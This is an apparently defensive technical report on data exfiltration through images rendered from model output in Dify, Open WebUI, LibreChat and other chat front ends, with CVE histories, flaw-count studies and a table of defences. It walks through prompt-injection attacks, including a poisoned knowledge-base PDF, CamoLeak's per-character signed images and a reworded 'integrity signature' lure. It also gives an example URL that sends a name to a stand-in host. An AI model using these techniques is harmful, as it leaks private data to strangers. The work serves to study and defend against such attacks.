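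Mistral's changelog lists no reversal of the 2024 fix, but neither the changelog nor the overview of Vibe explains how the product now handles external images. A customer could find out by testing it with an image hosted on their own server. The charts and dashboards would need separate tests because they may use different display code.

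## Open-source chat interfaces and app builders

Mistral controlled Le Chat's front end, so one change protected every user. Many organisations instead run a front end that someone else wrote. Some install an open-source chat interface, such as Open WebUI, LibreChat or Lobe Chat, on their own server and connect it to a model. Others use Dify, an open-source app builder, to assemble a chatbot from ready-made blocks and publish it as a web page.

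If such a page leaks data through images, the organisation may seem to have inherited the flaw from the project. Inheriting a flaw can mean several things, each requiring a fix in a different place.

### What it means to inherit the flaw

An application inherits a flaw if the faulty code or setting came from another project. Suppose a recruitment agency's hiring assistant loads images from any server. This flaw has at least four possible explanations.

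| How the agency got the flaw | Where a correction would work |
|---|---|
| It installed an open-source interface whose renderer loads all images | In the interface, because one release can fix every installation that upgrades |
| Its developers used a shared markdown library that permits all image hosts by default | In the library's defaults or the agency's own settings |
| It built the assistant from a template with unsafe settings | In the agency's copy, because a new template helps only people who use it later |
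| Its developers decided to display images and didn't consider where the requests would go | In the agency's own code |

If an agency's developers made the rendering decision themselves, they repeated a common mistake rather than inheriting it from another project, so no update from another project will correct it.

Willison's *GitHub Copilot Chat* lists the same image flaw in ChatGPT, Google Bard, Writer, Amazon Q and Google's NotebookLM. Embrace The Red's *Cline* describes it in Cline, a coding agent that could leak files of secret keys this way, and VerSprite's *Data Exfiltration via Image Rendering Fixed in Continue* reports it in another coding assistant. These teams probably made the same choice separately, but some of them could have used the same markdown library. Open-source projects are easier to judge because only the source code, not the leak itself, can show which explanation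 is right.

LibreChat's description as an enhanced ChatGPT clone can mislead. The project imitates ChatGPT's appearance and features, but it cannot have copied the renderer because OpenAI doesn't publish the code of ChatGPT's front end.

### A user's name in a Dify image address

In December 2025, the security researcher veganmosfet demonstrated data exfiltration through image rendering in a Dify chatbot, in *Data Exfiltration via Image Rendering in RAG Chatbot Frontend*. The chatbot used retrieval-augmented generation (RAG), which searches a collection of documents for passages relevant to a question and adds them to the prompt. Dify calls this collection a knowledge base.

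The researcher started from a Dify template for this kind of chatbot, selected a knowledge base of two PDF files, connected the model GLM-4.6 and published the app. One PDF contained hidden instructions for the model to answer any question about "prompt engineering" with an image. The image's address ended in `n=$NAME`, and the model was to replace `$NAME` with the user's name from the chat.

When the user mentioned prompt engineering, Dify found the passage and added it to the prompt. GLM-4.6 then included the image in its reply, with the name in the image's URL, and the user's browser sent the name to an outside server as soon as it displayed the reply.

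An attacker needs only one document in a knowledge base that many people search; the user in this attack did not upload a file or add a web page. The hidden text does nothing until someone raises its subject, so a deployer who tests the chatbot with other questions will see normal answers. This attack targeted only a name, but an attacker could use the same kind of instruction to request anything in the conversation. A single demonstration doesn't show how often GLM-4.6 would comply.

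The deployer inherited this leak from Dify's front end, which contains the code that displays images. The template supplied the search step that lets a stranger's text reach the model, but a Dify app made from a different template should load the same image.

### What a Dify deployer could configure

Dify sends no content security policy (CSP) if its `CSP_WHITELIST` setting is blank, according to *XSS in Dify could lead to Workspace Takeover* (veganmosfet, 2026). Dify's documentation lists the setting as empty by default and describes it as "Additional domains to allow in Content Security Policy headers". A deployer might reasonably conclude from this description that Dify already sends a CSP and that an empty list is the strictest choice.

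A deployer therefore has to name at least one domain to switch the policy on. The documentation for the setting doesn't mention images, so the deployer should then test whether the policy blocks an image from an outside server. Dify's standard installation also puts the application behind the web server Nginx, where an administrator can add their own policy.

Two other protections in Dify don't stop the leak. By default, Dify refuses addresses that begin with `data:`, but an image leak uses an ordinary web address. Dify also sends its own outbound requests, including image downloads, through a proxy that blocks addresses on the private network. According to release notes for Dify's enterprise edition, this proxy has stricter defaults there. But the user's browser doesn't use the proxy, and the attacker's server isn't on the private network.

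The researcher recommends turning off markdown and HTML rendering or, failing that, restricting it with a strong CSP. Filtering documents before they enter the knowledge base helps, but the researcher advises deployers to assume that some hostile text will get through.

### What the Dify project changed

Dify's developers have fixed two script flaws in the code that draws charts and diagrams. According to OSV's *CVE-2026-21866* (2026), the first arose because Dify ran Mermaid, the flowchart notation, with its security level set to "loose", which let a diagram in a chat run script. Version 1.11.2 fixed this flaw, rated 5.1 for severity.

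The second involved ECharts, a library that draws charts from a written description. Dify executed the description as JavaScript to get the chart's settings. A comment in Dify's source suppressed the warning that a code-checking tool would have given for that line.

An attacker could type a malicious chart into a public chatbot and wait for the workspace owner to open the chat logs. The chart's script could not read the owner's login cookie, but it could send Dify a request to invite the attacker's email address as an administrator. A model that had processed a poisoned document could also generate such a chart and leak the conversation. The researcher reported the flaw on December 23, 2025, and Dify published an advisory on February 11, 2026.

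OSV's *CVE-2026-26023* (2026) gives this flaw a severity of 5.3, which seems low for an attack that can give someone control of a workspace. The score rates the effect on Dify itself as none and the effect on other systems as low. The attack worked only on installations that kept the default blank CSP setting, which also exposed deployers to the image leak. Version 1.13.0 fixes the chart flaw.

Neither fix concerns ordinary markdown images. For the image leak, the researcher names no identifier, severity score or corrected version.

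Dify may also have inherited a permissive library default. Release notes for Dify's enterprise edition mention a fix to Streamdown, a markdown library made for AI chat. Streamdown's *Security* describes the library's default configuration as "permissive", with all image hosts allowed "to allow maximum functionality". Streamdown removes dangerous HTML by default, but *Security* tells developers to restrict image hosts when they display untrusted content. The release notes don't show whether Dify's developers did so.

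### A chart library's default in Open WebUI

Open WebUI provides better evidence of an inherited default. It can use Vega, a library that draws charts from written descriptions. According to OSV's *PYSEC-2026-3651* (2026), Open WebUI treated these descriptions as trusted and kept Vega's default loader, the part that fetches outside files. That default suits people who draw their own charts, but in Open WebUI the description could come from another user or a model.

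A malicious chart could make the browser contact an outside server in two ways. It could load its data from a URL on that server, which the browser would request as Vega began to build the chart. It could also use images instead of the usual dots. Vega then wrote the image's URL into the finished SVG, and the browser requested it when displaying the chart. A sanitiser would not remove this URL, because SVG files can legitimately contain image URLs.

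The advisory focuses on users who post a chart in a shared chat or channel, but it also lists model output that an attacker can influence. It says the flaw does not directly expose data on the server, which is true of a chart with a fixed address. But a model that followed hidden instructions could write Jane Doe's record into the address and leak it as in any other image leak.

The advisory also says the attack is not zero-click because the victim must open the message. But opening a message is ordinary use of a chat application, so the attack meets the definition of zero-click that applied to EchoLeak.

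The flaw, which has the identifier *CVE-2026-70480* (GitLab, 2026), affected Open WebUI versions 0.6.34 to 0.10.2 and has a severity score of 4.1. In version 0.11.0, Open WebUI replaced the loader with one that blocks external files. Charts can now use only data written into the description, and images must be embedded or come from Open WebUI's own site. Administrators only have to upgrade, because the safe behaviour is the default.

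### Similar flaws with different origins

GitLab's *CVE-2026-54011* (2026) reports that Open WebUI's file preview set Mermaid to the "loose" level, as Dify did, so a diagram in a markdown file could run script. Corgea's *Open WebUI* lists a severity of 8.7, compared with 5.1 for Dify's flaw, which had the same cause. Lobe Chat also had a Mermaid flaw, with a severity of 9.6 in OSV's *GHSA-4gpc-rhpj-9443* (2026), because a script in its desktop version could run programs on the user's computer.

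Each project set the "loose" option in its own configuration. For now, the better explanation is that the developers chose it independently. They might have copied it from the same sample code, but the advisories contain no evidence of this.

LibreChat had a flaw almost identical to AnythingLLM's mishandling of quotation marks in image descriptions, except that it came partly from marked, a shared markdown library, rather than from the application's own code alone. According to MITRE's *CVE-2026-54025*, LibreChat added its own image renderer to check whether an address was safe. If the address passed, LibreChat handed the image back to marked's built-in renderer, which in version 15.0.12 did not escape quotation marks in the description when used this way.

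LibreChat's safety check covered only the address, so an attacker could use an acceptable address and put a script in the description. The script ran inside a preview frame. OSV's *CVE-2026-54025* (2026) gives the flaw a severity of 5.4 and lists 0.8.4-rc1 as the first corrected version.

Other projects that use the marked library don't necessarily have this flaw, because it depended on how LibreChat's code interacted with the library. Developers who use marked would need to check whether their own code also replaces part of its image renderer.

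### Flaws in a project's own renderer

CIRCL's *GHSA-xq4x-622m-q8fq* reproduces the Lobe Chat code that displays unrecognised items as HTML. The code has separate branches for React components, SVG drawings, Mermaid diagrams and markdown.

The code branches that render SVG drawings, Mermaid diagrams and unrecognised items have all led to script flaws since September 2025. According to MITRE's *CVE-2025-59417*, an attacker could reach the SVG flaw through a malicious web page or a compromised tool. OSV rates that flaw's severity at 6.1 on one version of the standard scale and 6.8 on a newer one.

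According to SentinelOne's *CVE-2025-59417*, Lobe Chat fixed the SVG flaw by passing drawings through DOMPurify with strict lists of permitted elements and attributes. The fix changed only one branch of the code. If the developers had also made the final branch display unknown items as plain text, the later attack with the invented label "nebula" would have failed.

Open WebUI had a different flaw, in its own code. To display frames containing files from its own server, it checked whether a message included the opening text of such a frame and, if so, inserted the whole piece of HTML into the page. OSV's *GHSA-9f4f-jv96-8766* (2026) shows that an attacker could include the expected text, followed by a script that stole the user's access token from the browser's local storage.

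An attacker could spread the script by sharing a chat. If an administrator opened it, the attacker could use the stolen token to create a "function", which is Python code that Open WebUI runs on the server. Version 0.6.6 fixed the flaw, which has a severity score of 7.4. KoreLogic's *KL-001-2024-005* (2024) had already warned the project that version 0.1.105 could run JavaScript in a model's reply.

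| Project and versions | What the code displayed | Flaw | Source of the flaw | Identifier and severity | Default after the fix |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Open WebUI before 0.6.6 | HTML frames | Script | Its own code | CVE-2025-46719, 7.4 | No CSP |
| Lobe Chat before 1.129.4 | SVG drawings | Script | Its own code | CVE-2025-59417, 6.1 | DOMPurify cleans drawings |
| Dify before 1.13.0 | ECharts charts | Script | Its own code | CVE-2026-26023, 5.3 | No CSP |
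| LibreChat before 0.8.4-rc1 | Markdown images | Script | Its own code combined with a library | CVE-2026-54025, 5.4 | No CSP |
| Open WebUI 0.6.34 to 0.10.2 | Vega charts | Outside requests | A library's default | CVE-2026-70480, 4.1 | Charts load no outside files |

The scores come from two versions of the severity scale, so small differences between them mean little.

### Why Open WebUI rejected a report about images

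In March 2025 the bug bounty platform huntr published CVE-2024-7053, a vulnerability record about markdown images in Open WebUI, with a severity score of 7.6. According to the record, an image in a chat could send an administrator's login cookie to an attacker, who could then take over the account.

Open WebUI's *CVE-2024-7053* (2026) gives four reasons why this cannot happen: browsers send a cookie only to its own site, Open WebUI hides this cookie from scripts, Open WebUI also keeps it out of image requests that one site makes to another, and displaying a markdown image doesn't run a script. Huntr agreed to withdraw the record in August 2026, more than a year after publishing it.

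Open WebUI's maintainers are right that the browser's request to the outside server doesn't carry the cookie. But they don't dispute that the browser contacts the server, and image exfiltration doesn't need a cookie, so their reasons don't rule it out. An administrator who reads the page's advice, "No action required", could wrongly conclude that outside images are harmless.

The original report may have contributed to this confusion by claiming the wrong harm. Open WebUI's *Security Policy* requires reporters to demonstrate, in the default configuration, harm to someone other than themselves. A demonstration like the one in Dify, with another user's data in the address, would seem to qualify.

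Open WebUI has accepted a related report. OSV's *GHSA-j6w6-986j-2m2m* (2026) describes how one user could put the address of an external image in a profile picture, shared chat or note, making other users' browsers contact the server hosting the image. Version 0.9.3 fixed the flaw (CVE-2026-45317, severity 4.6). The attacker supplied the address directly, without involving a model.

### Reasons for leaving protections off

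LibreChat can send a CSP, but the policy is off by default. LibreChat's *HTTP Security Headers* explains that this is so that administrators can first check their existing integrations. This is reasonable, because a strict policy can break sign-in, file storage or embedded documents that depend on other hosts.

In LibreChat, setting `CSP_ENABLED=true` turns on a content security policy that only reports violations. The browser reports an image from an unapproved host but still requests it. To block the image, the administrator must also set `CSP_REPORT_ONLY=false`. By default, LibreChat instructs browsers not to reveal which site displayed an image, but the attacker still receives the data in the image's address.

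Open WebUI also sends no CSP unless the administrator configures one, according to Corgea's *Open WebUI vulnerable to stored XSS via OAuth picture claim*. The project says it designs the software for private, trusted networks and chooses defaults that make it easy to set up. It refers administrators who handle sensitive data to a guide on stricter settings. A private network does little to prevent data exfiltration through images, though, because employees' browsers can usually still reach the public internet.

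PromptArmor's *HuggingFace Chat Exfiltrates Data* describes a leak in HuggingChat, the chat service of Hugging Face, a company that hosts open AI models. A user uploaded a file of quarterly results, added a page of customer reviews and asked how to win back an unhappy reviewer. The page contained hidden text claiming that the reviewer needed to see a picture of the results. The model responded with a one-pixel image whose address contained the figures, and loading the image leaked them. PromptArmor reported this on December 1, 2025, and published it after Hugging Face's security team did not respond.

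A strict default is possible, as in OpenClaw, an open-source AI agent that people run on their own machines. Its browser interface has a CSP that administrators cannot turn off. According to OpenClaw's documentation, the browser loads images from OpenClaw and two fixed profile-picture services, and blocks other remote images. The drawback is that pictures from ordinary websites don't appear.

OpenClaw may still leak small amounts of data. By default, its server fetches an icon from each public website that a link points to. It requests a standard file name, so the request doesn't include private data from the rest of the link's address. But it does reveal the host name, where an attacker could put data. If OpenClaw fetches icons for links that the model writes, a short secret could leak without the user clicking anything. Administrators can turn the icons off.

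### What self-hosting changes

An organisation may install its own chat interface to keep private text on its own server. If the model also runs there, documents and conversations stay on the server unless a user's browser requests an outside image with some of that text in its address. This can happen even if the server has no internet connection, because the request comes from the user's computer. If an outside provider runs the model, the provider already receives the conversation, but image exfiltration can also send parts of it to a recipient the organisation did not choose.

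The hostile charts in Open WebUI could also make an employee's browser, which is inside the network, contact internal systems that the attacker could not reach from outside. Dify's proxy would not prevent this kind of attack because it filters only the server's own requests.

Self-hosting also lets a deployer change the model without changing how the page displays images. In Dify, the researcher connected GLM-4.6 through a standard type of API, and a deployer could replace it with another model. An agency that switches to a cheaper model could therefore make attacks more likely to succeed, even if its front end stays the same.

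Fixes also reach users more slowly than on a hosted service such as Le Chat. Dify's fix for ECharts protects a self-hosted workspace only after an administrator upgrades to version 1.13.0. Open WebUI supports only its current main version, so administrators generally have to accept all the other changes in a new release to get a security fix.

Administrators also have to learn that a fix exists. Dependabot, a GitHub tool, warns developers when their projects use software with known flaws. It depends on complete records in GitHub's advisory database. The US vulnerability database listed Open WebUI's HTML frame flaw in May 2025, but GitHub didn't review its entry until July 2026, so anyone who relied on Dependabot probably received no warning for 14 months.

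Open WebUI published 19 more advisories in September 2026. Another organisation, VulnCheck, then registered the flaws before GitHub did, and the resulting entries in GitHub's database did not list the affected versions. According to Open WebUI, none of the entries had triggered a Dependabot alert as of November 15, 2026.

Open WebUI now publishes a security advisory only after GitHub assigns it an identifier, which currently happens four weeks or more after the fix is released. The maintainers argue that this gives administrators time to upgrade and ensures that the advisory is accurate. But the fix is public as soon as it is released, so attackers can study it during those weeks, while administrators may not know that the upgrade is urgent.

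OSV's *PYSEC-2026-2731* (2026) describes a script flaw in Open WebUI's spreadsheet preview that the developers fixed in version 0.8.0 and later reintroduced. An administrator who has tested an installation with a hostile image and a hostile script therefore needs to repeat both tests after each upgrade.

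## What vulnerability records count and miss

The advisories on Open WebUI, Lobe Chat, LibreChat and Dify show that rendering flaws recur in popular software, but not how many chat products would leak a person's private data to a stranger. Two research teams have counted published flaws in software for language models, and their counts come closest so far to measuring this.

### A count of 529 flaws

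Wang, Zhao and colleagues (2025), in *SoK*, collected 529 vulnerabilities reported between January 2023 and October 2024. They searched vulnerability databases, the bug bounty platform huntr and security companies' publications for reports about 567 popular open-source projects on GitHub. Two of the researchers then labelled the cause of each flaw by hand.

The paper's figures differ between versions, but the total is the same in the two versions below, so the team evidently relabelled some of the flaws.

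| | Earlier version | Current version |
|---|---|---|
| Projects with a recorded flaw | 75 | 77 |
| Vulnerabilities | 529 | 529 |
| Cross-site scripting (XSS) | 33 (6.2%) | 31 (5.9%) |
| Failure to validate model output | 28 (5.3%) | 24 (4.5%) |

Neither of the last two rows measures unsafe rendering. The XSS row includes scripts from any source, such as a name typed into a form. The row on model output covers every sink, and one of its examples is a flaw in LangChain, a library for building on language models, that let an attacker's words become a database query. Only three of the 24 flaws in the current version are XSS. That is 0.6% of the whole collection. There is no category for image leaks.

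The earlier version also gives a much larger figure, 25.1%, for the share of flaws due to "improper neutralization". This category covers all 133 injection flaws, including ordinary SQL and operating system command injection. Only 28 of them, about a fifth, involved model output. The figure is easy to misread because the category sounds like OWASP's improper output handling, and the paper's introduction mentions generative outputs straight after it.

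The count also depends on where people looked. Before the final screening, 397 of the 597 candidate reports (66%) came from huntr. A project that attracts more bounty hunters will collect more entries even if its code is no worse, so AnythingLLM's 49 entries in the earlier version, compared with Open WebUI's seven, don't mean that it is seven times as dangerous.

### A sample of 100 advisories

In *LLM-Enabled Open-Source Systems in the Wild*, Shifat, Baburaj and colleagues (2026) searched a later and narrower source, GitHub's advisory database, for terms such as "openai" and "langchain". They found 295 advisories published between January 2025 and January 2026. Nineteen (6.4%) were for XSS, close to the share that Wang and colleagues found.

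The researchers excluded 35 advisories about packages that had little to do with language models, then drew 100 of the remaining 260 at random. Two of the researchers labelled each advisory in the sample with one or more of OWASP's 2025 categories.

Before the two annotators settled their differences, their agreement was 0.76 on Cohen's kappa, which corrects for chance agreement, and 0.95 on Gwet's AC1, a similar measure that is less sensitive to rare labels. On both scales, 1 means perfect agreement. The gap is unsurprising because most OWASP categories don't apply to most advisories, so much of the agreement was about which labels to leave off. Both figures cover the whole exercise, so they don't measure how reliably the annotators recognised improper output handling.

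Of the 100 sampled advisories, 12 were labeled as improper output handling, compared with 44 for supply chain risks (flaws in components that come from someone else), 20 for excessive agency and 18 for prompt injection. Given the sample size, the true number for improper output handling could be about 20 to 50 of the 260.

Most of the 12 probably did not involve displaying a page. Eight also had the excessive agency label, and the weakness that appeared most often with improper output handling was command injection, in which model text becomes part of a command that the software runs. XSS is missing from the paper's list of pairings that occurred four or more times, so it accounted for three at most.

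An image leak should have at least two labels, improper output handling and sensitive information disclosure. Only one advisory in the sample had both. If the annotators applied the labels consistently, the sample contains at most one image leak.

### Why the counts don't give a rate

Correctly labeling every advisory about an image leak would show only what share of published advisories involve such leaks. That share would rise if people reported fewer flaws of other kinds, even if no product had become less safe. Neither team ran the test needed to estimate how common the leak is, which would involve choosing a set of chat products without knowing which were vulnerable, making each display a reply with an image from a test server, and counting the requests that arrived.

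The records also have gaps, several of which affect image leaks in particular. Both studies cover open-source software, so the leaks in Writer, Notion AI, Superhuman and Le Chat could not appear in either. A company that runs its own service can change the display code without asking customers to install anything, so it has less reason to publish an advisory. Writer changed its display code in 2023 without publicly explaining why, and nobody knows how many other companies have done the same. Shifat and colleagues acknowledge that their data leaves out unreported weaknesses.

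Some flaws in hosted products get public identifiers. trackr.live's *The Model Writes the URL That Leaks Your Data* lists CVE-2025-32711 for EchoLeak and CVE-2026-42824 for SearchLeak. A study of open-source packages would still leave out both.

Weakness labels can also leave out a model's role in an attack. They come from the Common Weakness Enumeration (CWE), a numbered list of software mistakes. Shifat and colleagues give the example of spacy-llm, a package that connects a text-processing library to language models. Its advisory is correctly labeled as code injection, but none of the advisory's fields records that the attack can travel through prompt templates and text the model writes. Someone who searches the database for XSS therefore has to read every description to separate scripts that a model wrote from scripts that a person typed.

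CWE has an entry for unvalidated model output, CWE-1426, but it helps only if the people who file advisories use it. It isn't among the ten most frequent labels in the 295 advisories, so it appears at most 11 times.

A leak through a rendered image involves no script, so the XSS label would be wrong for it. One person might file the leak as a disclosure of sensitive information and another as a failure to validate output, so a search for either label would find only some of the cases. A keyword search can also miss cases, because an advisory about a general markdown library may not mention language models even if many chat products use the library.

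Rejected reports may leave no entry. Writer, HackerOne and OpenAI all rejected reports of image leaks at first, and those cases are public only because the researchers published them. Records can also overcount, as when huntr kept its disputed entry on Open WebUI's images for more than a year. OWASP's incident collection drew on public vulnerability databases too, so it probably has many of the same gaps.

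### Lists of affected products

The best evidence that image leaks are widespread comes from people who went looking for them. Rehberger calls the flaw "one of the most common" in applications built on language models, and the 2024 list of eleven affected products supports this in terms of breadth. Five of the products were Google's, three were Microsoft's, and the others came from OpenAI, Anthropic and Discord. These companies have large security teams, so inexperience explains little.

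Rehberger wrote about the leak in Google's Bard and Vertex AI in 2023, then in NotebookLM, AI Studio and Colab in 2024. Google evidently didn't remove it from all its other products after learning of it in one. The title of Rehberger's post on AI Studio mentions a "possible regression", meaning the flaw may have come back after a fix.

The list still doesn't show how common the flaw is, because it contains only the products in which Rehberger found it. Eleven failures would be much more alarming out of twelve products tested than out of 200. Rehberger also presumably chose products that seemed likely to be vulnerable.

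Later collections are longer but cover more than unsafe rendering. In August 2025 Rehberger published a report every day on security flaws in AI tools. By the middle of the month the reports had covered ChatGPT, Cursor, Devin, Claude Code and GitHub Copilot, among others, according to *The Summer of Johann* (Willison, 2025). All were vulnerable to some form of prompt injection, though not necessarily through images. By mid-2026 Willison's blog had 45 posts about data theft by prompt injection (*45 posts tagged “exfiltration-attacks”*). One of the newest describes a flaw that Ayush Paul found in the tool Claude uses to fetch web pages, rather than in image rendering.

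### Attacks outside research

Apparently, no one has publicly confirmed a case of a real attacker stealing data through an image in a model's reply. The known leaks are demonstrations. In December 2026, Cato AI Labs described ReLeak, a set of three zero-click attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot. Each began with an email that the victim didn't have to open, and one sent the data out through an image address. Microsoft fixed all three between September 17 and November 15, and Cato knew of no real attacks, according to AIAIAI.FYI's *Cato AI Labs details three ReLeak zero-click attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot* (2026).

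Real attackers use indirect prompt injection, but mostly for purposes other than leaking data. *Attackers Hide AI Prompt Injections Inside Phishing Emails* (Mascellino, 2026) reports on a campaign that the security company Barracuda analysed. Each email had a password-protected attachment for the human reader and hidden text for the reader's AI assistant. If the assistant obeyed the hidden text, its summary would present the email as legitimate or urgent. The attacker wanted the person to open the email and didn't need the assistant to leak anything. Barracuda did not say how widespread the campaign was.

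In April 2026 Google published the results of a search for hidden instructions in Common Crawl, an archive of the public web that saves two to three billion pages a month. Google's researchers searched for familiar phrases such as "if you are an AI", then had the Gemini model classify the matches and checked the results by hand. Most of the instructions they found were pranks, advertising or attempts to keep AI agents away. Only a few aimed to steal data, and the example Google showed was a website owner's experiment. Google found no significant use of the data-stealing prompts that researchers had published in 2025.

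This is good evidence that such attacks were not yet common on ordinary web pages, but we can learn little from it about private channels, because Common Crawl doesn't contain material like the email and uploaded CV used in the attacks on Superhuman and Notion AI. Google also found that malicious instructions rose by 32% between November 2025 and February 2026, although that category includes commands to delete a user's files as well as attempts to steal data.

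Security vendors have drawn stronger conclusions. Forcepoint reported live injections in the same week as Google, according to Help Net Security's *Indirect prompt injection is taking hold in the wild*. *Fooling AI Agents*, a March 2026 study by Palo Alto Networks' Unit 42, describes the technique as "actively weaponized", although "attempted" would have been more accurate. Its main case is a scam ad for military glasses, on a page with 24 hidden attempts to make an AI reviewer approve the ad. Unit 42 knew of no confirmed success against a working review system. The researchers also found a page designed to extract a company's contact data. They graded attacks by the attacker's intent because they had little information about which ones worked.

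Alibaba Cloud, a legitimate company, has also tried to get data this way. As part of its measures against abuse, it sent AI agents prompts that asked for local data and the agents' operating instructions. It has said it will stop, according to The Hacker News' *Alibaba Cloud Got Caught Prompt-Injecting AI Agents* (2026). Nothing suggests that an image carried any of the data.

Criminal interest in indirect prompt injection is growing. Proofpoint's *Notes from Underground* reported in July 2026 that sellers on closed forums were advertising tools for it, with ideas such as hiding instructions in calendar invitations. Google expects more attacks because AI systems have become more capable, and therefore more valuable as targets, and because attackers have begun to automate their work.

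The absence of confirmed thefts is weaker evidence of safety than it may seem, because an image leak is hard for the victim to notice. The recruiter's browser loads many images a day, and the request that carries Jane Doe's number goes directly to the candidate's server, not through the hiring assistant's. The candidate's server logs the request, but the candidate has no reason to report it. The recruiter's employer could discover the leak only by searching saved model replies or records of its staff's web traffic for private data in image addresses.

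## How to render model output safely

Victims rarely notice an image leak, so the integrator has to prevent it before the browser sends a request. The integrator can try to stop the model from writing a hostile image, or add code that refuses to load one.

### Telling the model not to write images

The easiest measure is to forbid external images in the system prompt, but an attacker can look for wording that gets around this instruction.

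In *The Framing Gap*, Rahman and Kim (2026) tested a similar instruction on an agent that held a secret token and read an attacker's web page. The agent had a tool for sending data, and its instructions named the only host that was allowed to receive the token. The test used a tool call instead of an image, but the model still had to choose whether to copy private text into something that would be sent to a stranger.

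OpenAI's GPT-4o ignored ten openly worded kinds of attack in all 200 trials. When the page instead called the token an "integrity signature", GPT-4o sent it in all 20 trials. Other wordings of the same trick failed completely, but an attacker who tried three wordings would succeed about 96% of the time.

The confidentiality instruction made little difference. Reworded attacks succeeded in 31.9% of trials with it and 38.1% without it, a smaller gap than the variation between runs of identical tests. A broader instruction that banned disclosure "in any form" cut the rate to zero, but with a version that listed specific behaviours and omitted that phrase, 48.8% of attacks succeeded. An integrator would have had trouble predicting this difference from the wording. Training wasn't a reliable fix either, since attacks still succeeded 32.5% of the time against SecAlign, a published training method.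 ChatGPT itself leaked nothing in 48 valid trials, but the researchers couldn't tell whether the model or the code around it prevented the leaks.

GPT-4o is an old model, and newer ones resist prompt injection better. *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (2026) describes a public competition where 464 people made 272,000 attempts against 13 leading models. About 3% worked, with rates ranging from 0.5% for Claude Opus 4.5 to 8.5% for Gemini 2.5 Pro. At 0.5%, a candidate who sent 200 CVs would have a 63% chance of at least one success if the attempts were independent. Attackers can do better by reusing what works, and some strategies in the competition worked in 21 of the 41 scenarios.

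Defences tested against fixed attacks can also look stronger than they are. *The Attacker Moves Second* (2025) found that attackers who adapt to a published defence can bypass it. In its competition for human attackers, an attack counted only if the agent also finished the user's task, so a victim might not have noticed anything wrong.

A rule in the display code prevents the image leak more reliably than model training because, like Mistral's fix for Le Chat, it doesn't need to recognise the attack. Model training is still worth having because a display rule doesn't prevent a biased hiring recommendation or a harmful tool call.

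### Eight defences in code

| Defence | What it stops | What it leaves open | What it costs |
|---|---|---|---|
| Showing markdown as plain text | Automatic requests and scripts | Addresses the user copies into a browser | Headings, tables and links |
| Dropping images | Image requests | Links, and diagrams that load their own images | Useful pictures |
| Permitting only images the application produced | Image requests to outside hosts | Links | Code to create and store the images |
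| Host allowlist in the renderer | Image requests to unlisted hosts | Redirects, and listed hosts that pass data on | Upkeep of the list |
| CSP limiting image sources | The same, plus images the renderer missed | Links, and listed hosts that pass data on | Testing, since a strict policy can break features |
| Fetching images through a server | Exposure of the user's IP address and browser | Data in the image's address | Running the server |
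| Asking before loading | Silent requests | Users who agree without reading | Interruptions |
| Sanitising HTML | Scripts | Ordinary images and links | Some HTML features |

Dropping images works only if the integrator does it in every component that renders output. Lee and colleagues exploited a diagram renderer that loaded an image from inside a Mermaid diagram, which a filter on markdown images would have missed.

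An application can permit only its own images by having the model write a short name, such as `chart-17`, instead of an address. The application's code looks up that name among the charts it has produced and supplies the address. Because no text from the model becomes part of the address, the address can't contain Jane Doe's record.

### Allowlists in the renderer and the browser

An allowlist in the renderer checks the address in the reply before creating the image, but it doesn't check later redirects. If a permitted site forwards visitors to any address they supply, the data still reaches the attacker. The documentation of *harden-react-markdown*, an add-on for the react-markdown library, therefore recommends permitting a folder such as `https://example.com/images/` rather than a whole site. It says in one place that the add-on doesn't resolve `/../`, which can lead out of the folder,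 and in another that it does. The integrator should make sure the image server refuses addresses containing `/../`.

The browser applies a content security policy (CSP) to every image on the page, whether it came from markdown, a diagram or a stylesheet, and checks again if a server redirects the request. After a redirect, it checks only the host and ignores the path, according to trackr.live. Vercel's *Building secure AI agents* treats a CSP as an extra layer behind output sanitising because integrators find CSPs hard to apply consistently. Using both makes sense because a mistake in one then doesn't cause a leak by itself.

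Both depend on a good list of approved hosts. Writer and Superhuman approved hosts that outsiders could use, and Salesforce approved a domain it no longer owned. According to Willison, researchers registered the expired domain and received data about sales leads from Salesforce's AI agent. The default list for the browser tool in Google's coding program Antigravity included webhook.site, a service that shows users the requests sent to them.

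An approved host may also receive private data without any attacker involved. QuickChart, for example, draws a chart from a description in the image's address. If the hiring assistant used it for a salary chart, QuickChart would receive the salaries.

trackr.live suggests finding out which hosts an application needs by running the CSP in report-only mode long enough to include rare tasks, such as quarterly reports. The policy blocks nothing in that mode, so the renderer has to block unsafe content in the meantime.

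### Fetching images through a server

Suppose the hiring assistant's renderer sends every outside image through a proxy. The address in the page becomes:

`https://hiring.example/proxy?url=https%3A%2F%2Fimages.example%2Fp.png%3Fd%3DJane%2520Doe`

The recruiter's browser contacts only hiring.example, which the CSP permits. The proxy decodes the rest of the URL and requests the original address from the candidate's server. The candidate sees the proxy's IP address instead of the recruiter's, but still receives Jane Doe's name. Streamdown's *Security* includes sample code that rewrites URLs this way, but doesn't explain which addresses the proxy should refuse.

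A proxy can prevent this leak by accepting only addresses that existed before the model read untrusted content, because the model can't have written private data into them.

GitHub's image proxy, Camo, enforces a similar rule with signatures. When someone saves a document with an outside image, GitHub replaces the image's address with a signed one, and Camo rejects any address without a valid signature. A model can't compute the signature, so it can't create a valid new address containing a secret.

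Legit Security's *CamoLeak* describes how a researcher got around this in June 2025. The researcher had GitHub sign one address for each letter and symbol, then hid the list in a comment on a proposed code change. The comment also contained instructions for GitHub's Copilot Chat to spell out private text as a row of invisible one-pixel images. As the victim's browser loaded the images in order, the researcher's server received the text one character at a time. The attack extracted the description of an undisclosed security flaw from a private project.

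With *n* prepared addresses, each request can carry up to log₂ *n* bits. A list of 64 addresses gives six bits, enough for one character from a set of 64, so Jane Doe's 21-character record would take 21 requests. According to Willison, GitHub fixed an earlier leak in Copilot Chat in 2024 by blocking images from untrusted domains. After CamoLeak, it stopped displaying images there altogether.

OpenAI uses a different test for whether an address is already known. Its crawler records public addresses without access to anyone's conversations, and ChatGPT automatically loads only addresses that exactly match a record. The company rejected a simple list of trusted sites because those sites can redirect to others, and because frequent warnings teach people to click through them. An attacker can still spell out text by using a different public page for each character, and Embrace The Red notes that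 a larger blog probably already has the 36 pages needed for letters and digits. It suggests blocking repeat visits to an address within a session, which would force the attacker to prepare more pages.

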